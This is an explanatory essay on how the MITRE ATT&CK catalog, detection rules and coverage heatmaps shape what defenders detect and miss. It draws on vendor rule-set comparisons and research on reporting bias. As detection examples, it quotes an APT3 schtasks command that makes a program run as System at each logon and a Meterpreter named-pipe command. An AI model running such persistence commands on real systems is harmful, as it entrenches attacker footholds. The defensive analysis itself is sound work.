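# How Taxonomies of Adversary Behavior Shape What Defenders See and Miss

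## What a taxonomy of adversary behavior is and how defenders use it

A taxonomy of adversary behavior is a list of hostile actions sorted by purpose and method. The best known is MITRE ATT&CK, a free, public catalog of what intruders do to computer networks and inside them. It is maintained by the MITRE Corporation, a non-profit that runs research centers for the US government. Security teams use the catalog to decide which behaviors to watch for and to label their software's alarms. Many also use it to report how many of the known kinds of attack they could detect. Researchers have begun to draw up similar catalogs of misbehavior by AI agents (AI models that act through tools, such as running code or using websites), and they face many of the choices that MITRE faced.

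### Where the catalog came from

ATT&CK stands for Adversarial Tactics, Techniques, and Common Knowledge, as Strom explained in *ATT&CK 101* (2018). The project grew out of FMX, a research environment that MITRE ran from 2010 inside a working part of its own corporate network to test ways of detecting intruders who had already got in. One team imitated known attackers, and another searched the recorded activity for signs of them. Strom, Applebaum and colleagues wrote in *MITRE ATT&CK* (2018) that the main measure of success was "How well are we doing at detecting documented adversary behavior?" To answer that, both teams needed the same list of behaviors, which the attacking team used to plan its exercises and the defending team used to count what it had detected.

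MITRE wrote the first version of ATT&CK, which mostly covered Windows, in September 2013 and published it in May 2015 with 96 techniques under 9 tactics. MITRE later added Mac and Linux computers in 2017, cloud services in 2019 and industrial control systems in 2020.

The emphasis on behavior was practical, because behavior is harder for attackers to change than the "indicators of compromise" defenders had long searched for, such as the digital fingerprint of a known malicious file or the address of a known hostile server. An attacker who alters the file slightly gets a new fingerprint. But an intruder who wants a program to survive a restart still has to get the computer to start it again, and there are far fewer ways to do that than there are malicious files.

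The catalog has four levels. Here they are for one behavior, the creation of a scheduled task, which is an instruction to a computer to run a program at a set time or event:

| Level | What it describes | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Tactic | Why the attacker acts | Persistence: keeping a foothold in the network |
| Technique | How the attacker does it, in general | Scheduled Task/Job (T1053), on any operating system |
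| Sub-technique | A more specific way of doing it | Scheduled Task (T1053.005), on Windows |
| Procedure | What one attacker or tool did | The group APT3 created a task named "mysc" |

The levels nest less neatly than the table suggests, because a technique can serve several tactics and a single procedure can involve several techniques. Each sub-technique, though, has exactly one parent. MITRE added sub-techniques in 2020 because some techniques had become very broad while others described one narrow action, which made the full set hard to read. The parent technique here, MITRE's *Scheduled Task/Job* (2017), is still broad. It covers Windows, macOS, Linux, software containers and network devices, and one of its examples is a set of 2025 attacks in Poland in which the intruders scheduled weekly scripts on FortiGate network equipment.

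MITRE also keeps entries for attacker groups, malicious software and campaigns, and links them to the techniques they used with references to published reports.

### From an attacker's command to an analyst's alert

Ordinary software uses the Windows task scheduler all the time, for instance to check for updates. Attackers use it too. MITRE's *Scheduled Task/Job* (2019), the entry for the Windows sub-technique, records a command that came from a downloader used by APT3, a hacking group that security researchers track under that name:

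`schtasks /create /tn "mysc" /tr C:\Users\Public\test.exe /sc ONLOGON /ru "System"`

This creates a task named "mysc" that starts the program test.exe whenever someone logs on. The last part makes the program run under the System account, which has almost unlimited rights over the machine. If the victim restarts the computer, the attacker's program starts again at the next logon.

Detection depends on telemetry, the records of activity that a system produces. Windows can write a record, event 4698, each time someone creates a scheduled task. According to Microsoft's *4698(S): A scheduled task was created*, the record holds the account that made the request, the task's name and its full definition, including the program it will run. Microsoft recommends monitoring all of these events, especially on critical computers. It also advises watching for tasks at the top level of the scheduler's folder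 tree, where malware often puts them. APT3's command gave no folder, so it would have created the task "mysc" at that level.

The same action can leave other traces. MITRE's *Detection of Suspicious Scheduled Task Creation and Execution on Windows* (2025) lists five kinds of relevant record, including the start of a new process and changes to the Registry, the database where Windows keeps its settings. Most of these records help only if the defender has turned them on. Event 4698 also requires an administrator to enable an audit setting.

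A detection rule is a standing query over telemetry that raises an alert when a record matches. Elastic, a company that sells security-monitoring software, publishes its rules, including a very simple one called *A scheduled task was created*. Every five minutes, the software searches the last nine minutes of Windows records for a newly created task. The rule also has exclusions, which are conditions under which it does not alert. One excludes tasks created by the computer's own account, which Windows marks with a dollar sign at the end of the name. Another excludes sixteen task names or name patterns that belong to common products from HP, Microsoft, Google and others. That list does not include "mysc", so the rule would match if the downloader was running under a person's account.

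The rule's author also labels it with the identifier of the ATT&CK technique it is meant to detect. A public copy of the rule, detection.fyi's *A scheduled task was created*, has the labels T1053 and T1053.005. Virkud, Inam and colleagues found in *How does Endpoint Detection use the MITRE ATT&CK Framework?* that analysts typically assign such labels by hand, using their own judgment. Judgments differ even for this one behavior. Elastic files its rule under Persistence alone, while *Scheduled Task Creation Via Schtasks.EXE* (Roth, 2019), which looks for the same behavior in process records, is labeled with Persistence, Execution and Privilege Escalation. Both choices are defensible, since APT3's command runs a program, keeps it on the machine and gives it higher rights.

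Finally, the alert reaches an analyst. Elastic rates it low severity, with a risk score of 21 out of 100, because so many scheduled tasks are harmless. In its guide, Elastic advises the analyst to check whether the account is known, what the task will run and when, and what else happened around the same time. The answers would look suspicious for "mysc", which runs test.exe from a folder open to every user, with full rights, at each logon.

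The analyst may have very little time to get that far. *The Exclusion Ratchet* (Dhananjeyan and U, 2026) cites measurements from one security operations center that received between 24,000 and 134,000 alerts a day, of which 0.01 percent corresponded to true attacks. The label helps in a queue like that. An analyst who reads "Persistence" knows that the intruder, if there is one, is already inside and means to stay, and can start looking for how they got in.

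### Technique coverage and the heatmap

Once rules have labels, anyone can count them against the catalog. The usual figure is technique coverage:

**technique coverage = techniques with at least one labeled rule ÷ all techniques in the catalog**

Virkud and colleagues calculated the coverage of three commercial products, using rules collected in October 2022 and version 11 of ATT&CK, which had 191 techniques. Carbon Black had rules for 105 of them (55 percent), Splunk for 100 (52 percent) and Elastic for 92 (48 percent).

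A technique adds one to the numerator no matter how many rules detect it. A company that already uses Elastic's scheduled-task rule does not raise its coverage by adding Roth's, even though the two rules read different telemetry and one might catch what the other misses. The denominator also changes. ATT&CK now has 227 techniques, so a product with rules for 92 of them would cover 41 percent, down from 48, without having lost any rules.

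A heatmap turns the same count into a picture. MITRE lays out the catalog as a matrix, with a column for each tactic and cells for the techniques under it, and defenders color the cells. MITRE's free tool for this, ATT&CK Navigator, reads a file that gives each technique a score and sets a color scale. In *schtasks (S0111)*, MITRE's file for the Windows utility that APT3 used, the Scheduled Task sub-technique has a score of 1 on a scale from white at 0 to blue at 1. A coverage heatmap is made the same way from a defender's own rules. *Beyond the Heatmap* (Feffer, 2026) describes the common version as green for covered and red for not covered, with perhaps a few shades between. Because a technique appears in the column of every tactic it serves, one rule for scheduled tasks can turn three cells green.

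### The catalog in 2026

MITRE's *Version History* shows a new release every spring and autumn in recent years. The current version, 20, is dated October 13, 2026. According to MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for that month, the part that covers enterprise networks has 15 tactics, 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques. The technique count is only roughly comparable with the 96 of 2015, since MITRE reorganized many techniques when it introduced sub-techniques. The whole catalog, which also covers mobile devices and industrial control systems, describes 182 groups, 971 pieces of software and 61 campaigns. Version 20 added several techniques that involve AI, and a campaign entry for an AI-assisted breach of Mexican government systems.

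The larger change of the year came with version 19 on April 28. Until then, a single tactic, Defense Evasion, had covered the many ways attackers avoid detection. MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for April announced its split into Stealth and Defense Impairment. Positive Technologies, in *MITRE has released the scheduled ATT&CK Matrix v19 update* (2026), distinguishes the two by the attacker's intent. Under Stealth, the attacker blends in with normal activity, and the security tools keep running but don't detect the attacker. Under Defense Impairment, the attacker targets the tools themselves, for example by shutting them down or deleting logs. Some techniques belong to both.

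Stealth kept the old code, TA0005, and Defense Impairment got a new one, TA0112. So a dashboard built around TA0005 still worked after April 28 but counted a narrower set of behaviors, as D3 Security pointed out in *MITRE ATT&CK v19 Drops April 28*. Elastic's *Remap detection rules to MITRE ATT&CK v19* told customers how to find and relabel their own rules. Dhananjeyan and U report that the maintainers of the main public collection of rules in Sigma, a format that works across different companies' products, relabeled the whole collection in one commit the next day. The relabeling did not change what any rule could detect.

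It may have changed what people notice, though. D3 Security argued that most teams had not invested in detecting the absence of expected signals, such as logs that suddenly stop, and predicted that this gap would show up on every coverage dashboard once impairment had its own column. The vendor's forecast is untested, but the reasoning is plausible, because a team with many rules for detecting hiding and few for detecting sabotage could look well covered under the old tactic.

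### What defenders gain from it

The most obvious benefit is a shared vocabulary. MITRE's entry for Windows scheduled tasks lists well over a hundred examples of attackers using them, drawn from reports by many companies and government agencies. The examples include Stuxnet, the sabotage program discovered in 2010; the SolarWinds compromise, in which spies reached their targets through a software supplier; and recent ransomware. The investigators wrote for different readers and in different terms. A defender who knows the identifier T1053.005 can find all these cases in one place. The defender can also use it to ask a tester to try the behavior, or a supplier to detect it, without first agreeing on what to call it.

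Virkud and colleagues call ATT&CK "invaluable" for organizing scattered attack behaviors and giving alerts context, though they conclude that coverage is a poor measure of a product's ability to detect attacks. They also note that the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency advises analysts to map raw data to ATT&CK techniques when writing up threats.

A common catalog also lets people compare incidents that have little else in common. *Mapping AI-enabled cyber threats* (Guru, Moix and Klein, 2026) maps a year of AI-enabled attacks that Anthropic had investigated onto ATT&CK. Based on the results, the paper questions whether an attacker's technical sophistication or number of techniques is a good guide to how dangerous they are. That question would be hard to ask without an agreed way of counting techniques. However, Strom and colleagues advise against identifying a group from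 its techniques alone, because many groups use the same ones.

They were just as careful about coverage, which vendors and auditors have since used as a score. They wrote that ATT&CK is not a checklist and that covering every technique is unrealistic. Their example is ipconfig, a Windows command that displays a computer's network settings. Technicians run it constantly, so alerting each time would be excessive, and recording it may be enough. Yet a defender who records only ipconfig will miss an attacker who gets the same details through PowerShell, Windows' scripting tool. Scheduled tasks have the same problem, since an attacker can create one through PowerShell or by editing the Registry directly. Feffer's team at MITRE has begun to measure how many such variants a set of rules can observe.

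A variant can also appear in the data a rule checks and still raise no alert. MITRE's scheduled-task entry includes StrifeWater, malware that named its task "Mozilla\Firefox Default Browser Agent" followed by a string of characters. Elastic's rule excludes every task in the Mozilla folder whose name begins with those words, presumably because the real Firefox browser creates one. StrifeWater's task would therefore raise no alert from this rule. Another rule might catch it, but the heatmap cell for scheduled tasks would be green either way, so a reader could not tell from the heatmap whether this gap exists or how many other green cells have similar ones.

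## How behaviors enter the catalog and which are left out

A heatmap has cells only for behaviors that MITRE has listed. Before MITRE lists a behavior, someone has to notice an intrusion, investigate it and publish a report. The report then has to reach MITRE, and MITRE has to accept that it describes something new. Behaviors drop out at every step. *Mapping to ATT&CK from Narrative Reports* (Pennington, 2020), a MITRE training course for analysts, warns that not all possible techniques are documented, "nor will they ever be".

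### From an intrusion to an entry

An attack that nobody notices produces no report, and what people learn about the attacks they do notice depends on their vantage point. *You Can Tell a Cybercriminal by the Company they Keep* (2023) cites a comparison by Bouwman and colleagues that found little or no overlap between two leading threat intelligence vendors' indicators for the same 22 groups. Lists of techniques would probably overlap more, because behaviors change more slowly than indicators, but they also depend on the source's vantage point. Cyentia's *Multi-Source Analysis of Top MITRE ATT&CK Techniques* compared 22 public sources from 2022 and 2023. Companies that manage their customers' security or respond to incidents reported two to three times as many different techniques as sources that relied only on telemetry or only on public information.

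An investigator then reconstructs the attack from whatever records survive. Suppose APT3's scheduled task turns up on a computer that keeps its logs for only a week. The investigator can report the task, but perhaps not how the intruder got in. In the revised edition of its design paper, MITRE (2020) tells analysts to record a technique only if the report states it or the attack could not have happened any other way. This rule keeps guesses out, but it can also leave some of an intrusion's steps out of the catalog.

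"The vast majority of incidents discovered are not reported publicly," according to the design paper, and MITRE does not accept leaked or classified material as a substitute. That leaves mostly reports published by companies that sell security. According to Pennington's course, 92 percent of the reports behind the catalog's examples of group behavior came from security vendors, 5 percent from the press and 3 percent from governments. A MITRE staff member told Tripwire, a security company, that there was little public reporting on attacks on cloud services, so the team mostly talked to people who could see such attacks.

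MITRE's staff read new reports, and anyone can send suggestions through MITRE's web page *Contribute*. The main rule on that page is that the catalog includes only behavior that real attackers have used. This excludes hypothetical techniques and methods used only in laboratories or by red teams (testers who imitate attackers). MITRE gives priority to common behaviors with clear public references, and warns that it can't reply to every submission.

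Even a behavior that meets the rule may not get its own entry. MITRE can create a technique, create a sub-technique or widen an existing entry. Its staff consider, among other things, whether the behavior works differently from those already listed and whether defenders would need another way to detect or prevent it. One example in the design paper is SQL injection, a common attack in which someone enters database commands into a badly secured website. It has no entry of its own and falls under the broader technique Exploit Public-Facing Application. Widening entries keeps the catalog readable, but any detection rule for the old entry then counts as covering the new behavior too.

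The rule used to be looser, at least on paper. In 2020 MITRE distinguished four grades of evidence:

- **Reported:** public sources describe attackers using the behavior.
- **Reported, non-public:** only private sources describe its use, but the technique itself is publicly known.
- **Underreported:** attackers are probably using it, but for some reason nobody reports it.
- **Unreported:** no source, public or private, describes attackers using it.

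MITRE could once admit an unreported behavior if it looked useful and attackers seemed likely to adopt it. The *Contribute* page now rules that out, but MITRE's *Frequently Asked Questions* says the catalog also draws on public research into new techniques, because attackers often adopt them quickly. The FAQ is probably the older page, since it describes a catalog without the part on industrial control systems. If so, MITRE may have added some current entries under the looser rule.

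### Whom the reports describe

Because security companies write most of the reports, their reasons for publishing affect what MITRE can learn. Maschmeyer, Deibert and Lindsay argue in *A tale of two cybers* that these reports are mainly marketing. A company can't easily prove that its product works, but a detailed account of a dramatic attack shows how skilled its analysts are. They used public statements, earlier research and an interview with a researcher at one firm to identify three things that make an attack worth publishing: an unusual method, a prominent victim and a prominent attacker. Attacks on activists, journalists and charities would usually be left out on this basis, because these groups can rarely afford expensive security products and attackers can often reach them with cheap, familiar methods.

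A study of 629 commercial reports from 2009 to 2018 found that only 82 (13 percent) discussed a threat to civil society, and 22 (4 percent) made it their main subject. The companies named a government behind such a threat in 40 cases, and in 35 of them it was China, Russia or Iran. In a separate set of 71 reports by independent research centers, more cases came from other governments, including Ethiopia, Mexico and Saudi Arabia, than from those three.

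These percentages don't prove neglect by themselves, since nobody knows what share of all attacks target civil society. The paper acknowledges that the independent centers, including Citizen Lab, which Deibert directs, are biased too, because they look for these victims. The paper's case study of APT28, a hacking group that US prosecutors have tied to Russian military intelligence, is stronger evidence, because some of the group's targets are known. In one phishing campaign linked to APT28, Citizen Lab found that 21 percent of the targets belonged to civil society, just behind governments at 24 percent. SecureWorks, a commercial firm, put the share at 36 percent in a similar campaign. Yet of 57 commercial reports on the group, only 15 mentioned civil society and two focused on it.

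A catalog of behaviors, however, can include a technique even when reports neglect some of its victims. If a bank and an activist fall for the same kind of phishing email, a report on the bank is enough to get the technique listed, though the missing report on the activist makes it look rarer than it is. A technique is more likely to be left out when attackers use it mainly on people whom few companies write about. APT28's apparent targets included a journalist whose stolen emails the attackers leaked after inserting false material. None of the commercial reports described this technique, and only one briefly mentioned alleged alterations.

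The companies' preference for unusual methods probably helps MITRE find new techniques, but it misleads anyone who uses the reports to judge which techniques are common. MITRE's *ATT&CK Sightings* lists five biases in its sources. Reports favor techniques that are novel, that the publisher can observe, or that come easily to the author's mind. They also favor the customers of the most prolific publishers and victims who are more willing to report. In the 22 sources that Cyentia compared, 36 percent of the catalog's techniques and 85 percent of its sub-techniques never appeared. MITRE had found grounds to list all of them, so a technique's absence from two years of published statistics is weak evidence that attackers don't use it.

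MITRE responded by asking defenders for raw sightings of techniques. Its Center for Threat-Informed Defense has since analyzed more than a million security events from companies including Fortinet and Verizon. These data don't depend on which stories get published, but they still include only events that were detected. The Center notes that an apparent rise in a technique may mean that defenders have become better at detecting it. Zeltser, giving the industry's view to Cybersecurity Dive, suggested that society should look to publicly funded organizations if it finds company reporting insufficient.

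### How long a new behavior waits

A catalog that requires evidence of use has to lag behind new behavior, because someone must be attacked before anyone can report it. The delay has four parts:

**listing delay = time to notice + time to investigate and publish + time for MITRE to review + wait for the next release**

Nobody appears to have measured the total delay between attackers' first use of a behavior and its publication in the catalog. The catalog's dates don't help much, since they show when MITRE created an entry, not when attackers first used the behavior. Only the last part of the delay, from acceptance to release, is easy to estimate. Versions 19 and 20 came out 168 days apart, so a behavior that MITRE accepted at a random time between them would have waited about 12 weeks on average for the next major release.

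Noticing a behavior can take far longer. *A Graph-Based Approach for Mapping Kernel-Level Telemetry to MITRE ATT&CK* (2026) uses the SolarWinds compromise as its example. The intruders had been inside for roughly 14 months when the attack became public in December 2020. Victims had traces in their logs, including suspicious network requests and irregular login tokens, but analysts did not work out which techniques these belonged to until months after the initial compromise. This was a delay in recognizing an attack, and many of its 70 or more techniques may already have been in the catalog, but any new technique would have had to wait at least as long to be added.

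*A Decade of Healthcare Cyber Threats* (Rahi, Siddika and colleagues, 2026) calculated the length of five sustained campaigns recorded in ATT&CK. The mean was 517 days, and four lasted more than a year. The sample is very small and excludes campaigns that nobody has exposed. The figures also don't measure how long the campaigns went unnoticed.

A taxonomy can be late to include a well-documented behavior if its designers had a different goal in mind. MITRE added the Impact tactic, which covers destroying, disrupting or falsifying data and systems, in 2019, four years after it published the catalog and nine years after the discovery of Stuxnet. Sabotage was already well known, but MITRE had built the original tactics around intruders who steal information.

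### The thin record of an attack's first steps

Rahi and colleagues' main subject was the set of attackers that target healthcare. They took 25 groups, 14 malware families and 5 campaigns with documented healthcare targets, and collected every technique that ATT&CK linked to them, 333 in all, including sub-techniques. MITRE had written detection guidance for 294 of these (88 percent). They also counted each technique's "data sources", the kinds of telemetry that MITRE listed as useful for detecting it. The averages differed greatly between the first and last stages of an attack:

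| Tactic | What the attacker is doing | Techniques in the study | Mean data sources per technique |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reconnaissance | Gathering information about the target | 21 | 0.67 |
| Resource Development | Acquiring tools, accounts and servers | 26 | 1.59 |
| Exfiltration | Taking data out of the network | 10 | 5.0 |
| Impact | Destroying, disrupting or falsifying | 7 | 4.45 |

Scheduled Task had seven data sources. Tool, the sub-technique for obtaining software to use in an attack, had one, although the study's table links it to 16 of the 44 attackers (14 in its text).

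Rahi and colleagues say that early steps are poorly recorded because they leave the fewest traces and lead to the fewest published reports. This explanation fits Reconnaissance well. Under their ranking method, no Reconnaissance technique can have had links to more than two of the 44 attackers, and it is hard to believe that so few of them studied their targets first. The explanation fits Resource Development less well, as the figure for Tool shows. Investigators who find a tool on a victim's computer can infer that the attacker obtained it somewhere, even if nobody saw that happen.

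The shortage of data sources for early steps is more likely due to much of this activity happening outside the victim's network. Someone who reads a hospital's staff directory on another website, or buys a hacking tool, may leave traces with other companies but none in the hospital's logs. A shortage of reports doesn't directly explain the gap, because MITRE can list the records that would reveal a behavior without knowing how many groups use it. Virkud and colleagues suspected a similar cause when they found that three commercial products together had rules for only 4 of 10 Reconnaissance techniques and 2 of 7 in Resource Development. If they are right, more reporting would improve the catalog's account of early steps but give hospitals little more data for detecting them.

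The counts are a poor measure of how well anyone detects attacks, since one good record can be more useful than five poor ones. The study's claims about change over time are even weaker. Rahi and colleagues found that Persistence fell from 11.2 percent of technique use to zero between 2017 and 2024, and inferred that attackers had moved to stealthier methods. But they dated each technique by when MITRE created the entry for the earliest attacker linked to it. If the yearly shares are based on those dates, a persistence technique already recorded for a 2017 group could not count again in 2024, even if many attackers were still using it. The researchers themselves caution that their trends partly reflect the pace of publication.

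The catalog has also changed since the study, which used version 15.1. The next release, version 16 in October 2024, brought what MITRE called a "dramatic expansion" in the number of techniques with detection notes and analytics. In version 18, a year later, MITRE replaced the old guidance with "detection strategies" and deprecated data sources. So nobody can repeat the count in the same form on the current catalog, and the 88 percent figure is out of date. Some of the gap probably remains, though, because the early steps still mostly happen where victims can't see them.

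### What the observed-use rule buys and costs

MITRE argues that requiring observed behavior keeps the catalog tied to threats defenders are likely to meet. Researchers can invent far more attacks than real intruders will carry out, because many are too difficult or not useful enough. A team that tried to prepare for all of them would have less time for phishing and stolen passwords. The rule also lets readers check an entry against its references and gives MITRE a reason to turn down vendors, who have an interest in listing any threat their product detects. Maschmeyer and colleagues describe exaggerated threats in commercial reports as a well-established problem.

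The current rule hurts defenders most when a behavior is new. MITRE itself says that attackers quickly adopt published techniques, which is a good argument for listing some of them early, while defenders still have time to prepare. For now, defenders have to get that warning elsewhere, such as from the original research.

The rule also favors behaviors that get attackers caught. *Attackers reveal their arsenal* (2024), a study of techniques in threat reports, acknowledges that its ATT&CK data contain only the techniques that experts identified and reported, so attackers may have used others. A method that reliably escapes notice could remain unlisted for years. There is no good estimate of how many such methods exist, and defenders cannot tell from the catalog whether a missing method is undetected or unused.

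MITRE could reduce this drawback by listing plausible but unobserved behaviors separately, with a clear label for the strength of the evidence. It would then have to decide which of the many possible attacks were plausible enough to include, a judgment it mostly avoids under the observed-use rule. The option of a separate list also matters for catalogs of AI agent behavior.

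## Which techniques get detection rules and how they are labeled

After MITRE lists a technique, someone still has to write a rule to detect it and decide how to label that rule. Outsiders can rarely check either step, because most companies that sell detection software keep their rules secret. In August 2024, Virkud and colleagues presented what they believe was the first independent comparison of rule sets, covering three commercial sets they were able to read and one public set. The rules date from October 2022, and no later study appears to have repeated the whole comparison.

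### Four rule sets from October 2022

All four sets mainly detect activity on endpoints, such as laptops and servers. Splunk and Elastic publish their rules openly. Carbon Black shows its rules to customers, and the researchers got access through an educational license. Sigma's rules come from hundreds of contributors, so the researchers reported its results separately in case its quality control was less uniform. They left out rules without ATT&CK labels and, for the commercial products, rules the vendor had retired or not yet finished. They also ignored sub-techniques, because the vendors did not commonly use them as labels.

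| Rule set | Labeled rules | Techniques covered (of 191) | Technique coverage | Coverage counting only high-rated rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Carbon Black | 867 | 105 | 55% | 46% (by severity) |
| Splunk | 911 | 100 | 52% | 25% (by risk) |
| Elastic | 473 | 92 | 48% | 26% (by risk) |
| Sigma | 2,195 | 151 | 79% | 62% (by criticality) |

The last column counts a technique only if the maintainers rate at least one of its rules high or critical. This cuts Splunk's and Elastic's coverage by about half. One excluded Splunk rule alerts whenever someone runs curl or wget, two common programs for downloading files. Attackers use them to bring in their own tools, so the rule is labeled Ingress Tool Transfer. But administrators use them all the time, and Splunk gives the rule a confidence score of 10 out of 100 and a risk score of 1. In an ordinary coverage count, that rule alone would be enough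 to count the technique as covered.

The ratings in the last column measure either severity or risk. Severity is the damage an attack would do if the alert were real, while risk combines severity with confidence that the alert is real. Carbon Black publishes only severity. Elastic publishes both, and its coverage falls to 26 percent on either measure. Carbon Black may therefore have rules for serious attacks across more of the catalog, or it may just rate similar rules as more severe.

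A rule with a low rating can still be useful, because several weak alerts from the same computer can add up to strong evidence of an attack. But a busy analyst will probably look at a low-rated alert late or never. Ratings also vary widely among rules for the same technique, so the technique's name is a poor guide to how urgent an alert is.

Whether people count tactics or techniques matters even more than the ratings. Each commercial product had at least one rule for 13 or 14 of the catalog's 14 tactics, so its coverage looks nearly complete by that count, but it looks about half complete when people count techniques.

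### What companies actually run

CardinalOps (2024), a company that sells software for managing detection rules, examined its customers' SIEMs, the systems that collect and search a company's logs. On average, these systems had rules for 19 percent of ATT&CK techniques, although they already collected enough data to support rules for 87 percent. Help Net Security's *Enterprise SIEMs miss 79% of known MITRE ATT&CK techniques* gives an average of 21 percent for the following year. It also reports that 13 percent of the rules could never raise an alert, for instance because a log lacked a field that the rule needed.

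CardinalOps has a commercial interest in finding gaps, and its customers may not be typical. Still, its figures don't contradict the study's 48 to 55 percent, because Virkud and colleagues counted the rules vendors offered, while CardinalOps counted the rules customers had in place. A vendor's coverage is closer to an upper limit than an estimate of what a customer gets from that vendor's rules.

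The vendors' own collections have grown too. Long and Evans (2026), in *Evolution of Log-Based Detection Rules in Public Repositories*, counted 2,310 active rules in Splunk's public collection in April 2026, more than twice the 911 in the earlier study. The two counts used different criteria, but that probably doesn't explain such a large difference. The 52 percent figure is therefore not a reliable measure of Splunk's coverage today, because the new rules may cover techniques that had none or add to those that already had plenty.

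### Products with similar priorities

In 2022, at least, vendors spread their rules very unevenly across techniques. Each commercial product had 19 to 25 techniques with a single rule and three or four with more than 50. Carbon Black had 142 rules (about one in six of its total) for System Binary Proxy Execution, in which an attacker runs malicious code through a trusted program already on the computer. Scheduled Task/Job was also among the ten techniques with the most rules across the three products.

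To find out whether the vendors favored the same techniques, Virkud and colleagues ranked the techniques in each product by their share of its rules. They then calculated Spearman's rank correlation for each pair of products:

**ρ = cov(R(A), R(B)) ÷ (σ of R(A) × σ of R(B))**

Here R(A) and R(B) are the techniques' ranks in products A and B, cov is the covariance of the two sets of ranks, and σ is the standard deviation. The result is 1 if both products rank the techniques in the same order, about 0 if the orders are unrelated, and −1 if one order is the reverse of the other. For example, if one product ranked five techniques 1, 2, 3, 4, 5 and another ranked them 2, 3, 1, 4, 5, the correlation would be 0.7.

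The actual values were close to that, at 0.634 for Carbon Black and Splunk, 0.639 for Splunk and Elastic, and 0.744 for Carbon Black and Elastic. Correlations this high would be very unlikely if the orders were unrelated (p < 0.001 for each pair). Sigma's correlations with the commercial products were slightly higher, from 0.701 to 0.793, even though its rules came from a large community and covered far more techniques.

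The products also tended to miss the same techniques. Carbon Black had no rule for 45 percent of the techniques, Splunk for 48 percent and Elastic for 52 percent. If each had chosen its techniques independently, about 11 percent (0.45 × 0.48 × 0.52), or 21 techniques, would have had no rule in any of the three. The actual number was 53, or 28 percent, so a customer who bought all three products would have had rules for 72 percent of the techniques.

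Although the three products had similar priorities overall, their overlap varied a lot by tactic. For both Privilege Escalation and Impact, at least one product had a rule for 12 of the 13 techniques. All three had rules for 11 of the Privilege Escalation techniques but only one of the Impact techniques.

None of this explains why the vendors made similar choices. They may face the same attacks, read the same reports or work within the same limits on what endpoint software can record. The catalog may also influence them, since the tactics with the most listed techniques were among those where the products covered the most techniques. But those tactics had more techniques to cover, so this could happen without any influence from the catalog.

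### Why 53 techniques had no commercial rule

To understand the shared gaps, three researchers read MITRE's descriptions of the 53 techniques and its suggestions for detecting them. Each wrote down likely reasons why the techniques had no rules. They then agreed on a common set of reasons and discussed every technique until they reached consensus. They could assign several reasons to one technique.

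The researchers didn't ask the vendors why they had written no rule, so the reasons are inferences from MITRE's text. MITRE's *Analytic Coverage Comparison* (2024) provides a partial check. It lists the number of Elastic, Splunk and Sigma rules for each technique in January 2024, 15 months after the study's snapshot. The table gives those numbers for one example of each reason.

| Inferred reason | Techniques | Example | Rules in January 2024 |
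|---|---|---|---|
| The known ways of detecting it don't work well | 21 | Execution Guardrails: malware that runs only on a computer meeting set conditions | None |
| The target is not an endpoint | 13 | Compromise Infrastructure: taking over servers or other systems to use in an attack | Sigma 2 |
| Detection depends on the customer's own software | 9 | Steal Application Access Token | Elastic 3, Sigma 10 |
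| MITRE's detection advice is vague | 9 | Data from Configuration Repository | None |
| It happens on someone else's systems | 8 | Gather Victim Org Information | None |
| Detection requires linking a chain of events | 4 | Modify Cloud Compute Infrastructure | Elastic 2, Sigma 1 |
| It happens in hardware or firmware | 3 | Hardware Additions | Splunk 5, Sigma 2 |
| It involves removable media | 3 | Data from Removable Media | None |
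| It depends on human behavior | 1 | Phishing for Information | None |
| Unknown | 2 | Browser Information Discovery | Sigma 3 |

Execution Guardrails shows why the most common reason is hard to overcome. An attacker might have malware check a computer's name or language setting and run only if it matches, so that it stays inactive on a researcher's test machine. MITRE suggested watching for programs that gather such information, but warned that this is difficult because it depends on how the attacker builds the check. Many harmless programs read the same settings, so a rule broad enough to catch the attacker would raise constant false alarms. MITRE described its suggested detection as ineffective for 14 of the 21 techniques in this group, and the researchers judged it ineffective for the other seven.

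Some of the remaining reasons relate more to where the software runs. For instance, no endpoint rule could detect an attacker who studies a company's staff on social media. A vendor that wrote a rule for this technique anyway would raise its coverage without improving its product. This is the best argument against making full coverage a goal for endpoint software.

Other reasons for missing rules were less permanent. By January 2024, Elastic or Splunk had rules for three of the ten examples. MITRE may have counted some retired or unfinished rules that the study left out, but a few vendors had probably found ways to detect techniques that looked impractical to detect in 2022. Sigma had rules for 151 techniques in 2022, compared with 138 for the three commercial products combined. So at least 13 of the 53 techniques already had a public rule, though those rules may not have been good.

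A heatmap shows all of these gaps in the same color, but some call for a better rule, some for a different kind of product, and some for no action because the defender has no way to see the behavior.

### Different labels for the same threat

Where products do have rules, counting coverage relies on rule writers labeling the same behavior the same way. Virkud and colleagues tested this by looking for threats that more than one vendor had set out to detect. They searched the rules' descriptions for the names of malware, attacker groups, campaigns and software vulnerabilities, and checked the matches by hand. They found 191 threats (coincidentally the same as the number of techniques), 37 of which appeared in the rules of at least two products. They then compared the technique labels that the products used for each of those 37 threats.

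For 19 threats, no two products shared a technique label. The products agreed completely on one threat. Of the 296 labels across all 37 threats, 37 (12.5 percent) matched. Nine threats appeared in all three products, which agreed on 4 of those threats' 141 labels.

These totals probably overstate the disagreement. FIN7, one of the nine, is a criminal group that uses many methods. Splunk's rules for it had nine technique labels, Elastic's had three and Carbon Black's had two, with no overlap. But one vendor may have written a rule for the group's phishing emails and another for its data theft, in which case different labels would be correct. The researchers acknowledge this, and their stronger evidence comes from pairs of rules that detect the same action.

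In one such case, all three products had a rule for a trick used by Meterpreter, a program that testers and attackers use to control a computer. The attacker sets up a named pipe, a channel through which Windows programs exchange data, and borrows the identity of the account that connects to it. A single command published by Splunk would set off all three rules:

`cmd.exe /c echo 4sgryt3436 > \\.\pipe\5erg53`

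Elastic and Carbon Black labeled their rules Access Token Manipulation, which describes the borrowed identity. Splunk gave its rule two labels: Command and Scripting Interpreter, which describes the tool that ran the command, and Create or Modify System Process. All of these labels are reasonable, as were those on the scheduled-task rules.

Sometimes two techniques overlap, and vendors label rules for the same attack differently. CVE-2021-4034 is a flaw in pkexec, a Linux program that lets approved users run commands with administrator rights. Carbon Black labeled its rule for this flaw Abuse Elevation Control Mechanism. Splunk chose Exploitation for Privilege Escalation, and Elastic used that label plus another, Hijack Execution Flow. An attacker who exploits pkexec is both exploiting a flaw and abusing a program that controls administrator rights, so MITRE's definitions don't determine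 whether Carbon Black's or Splunk's label is right. A reader of either label would still learn that the attacker was trying to gain more rights.

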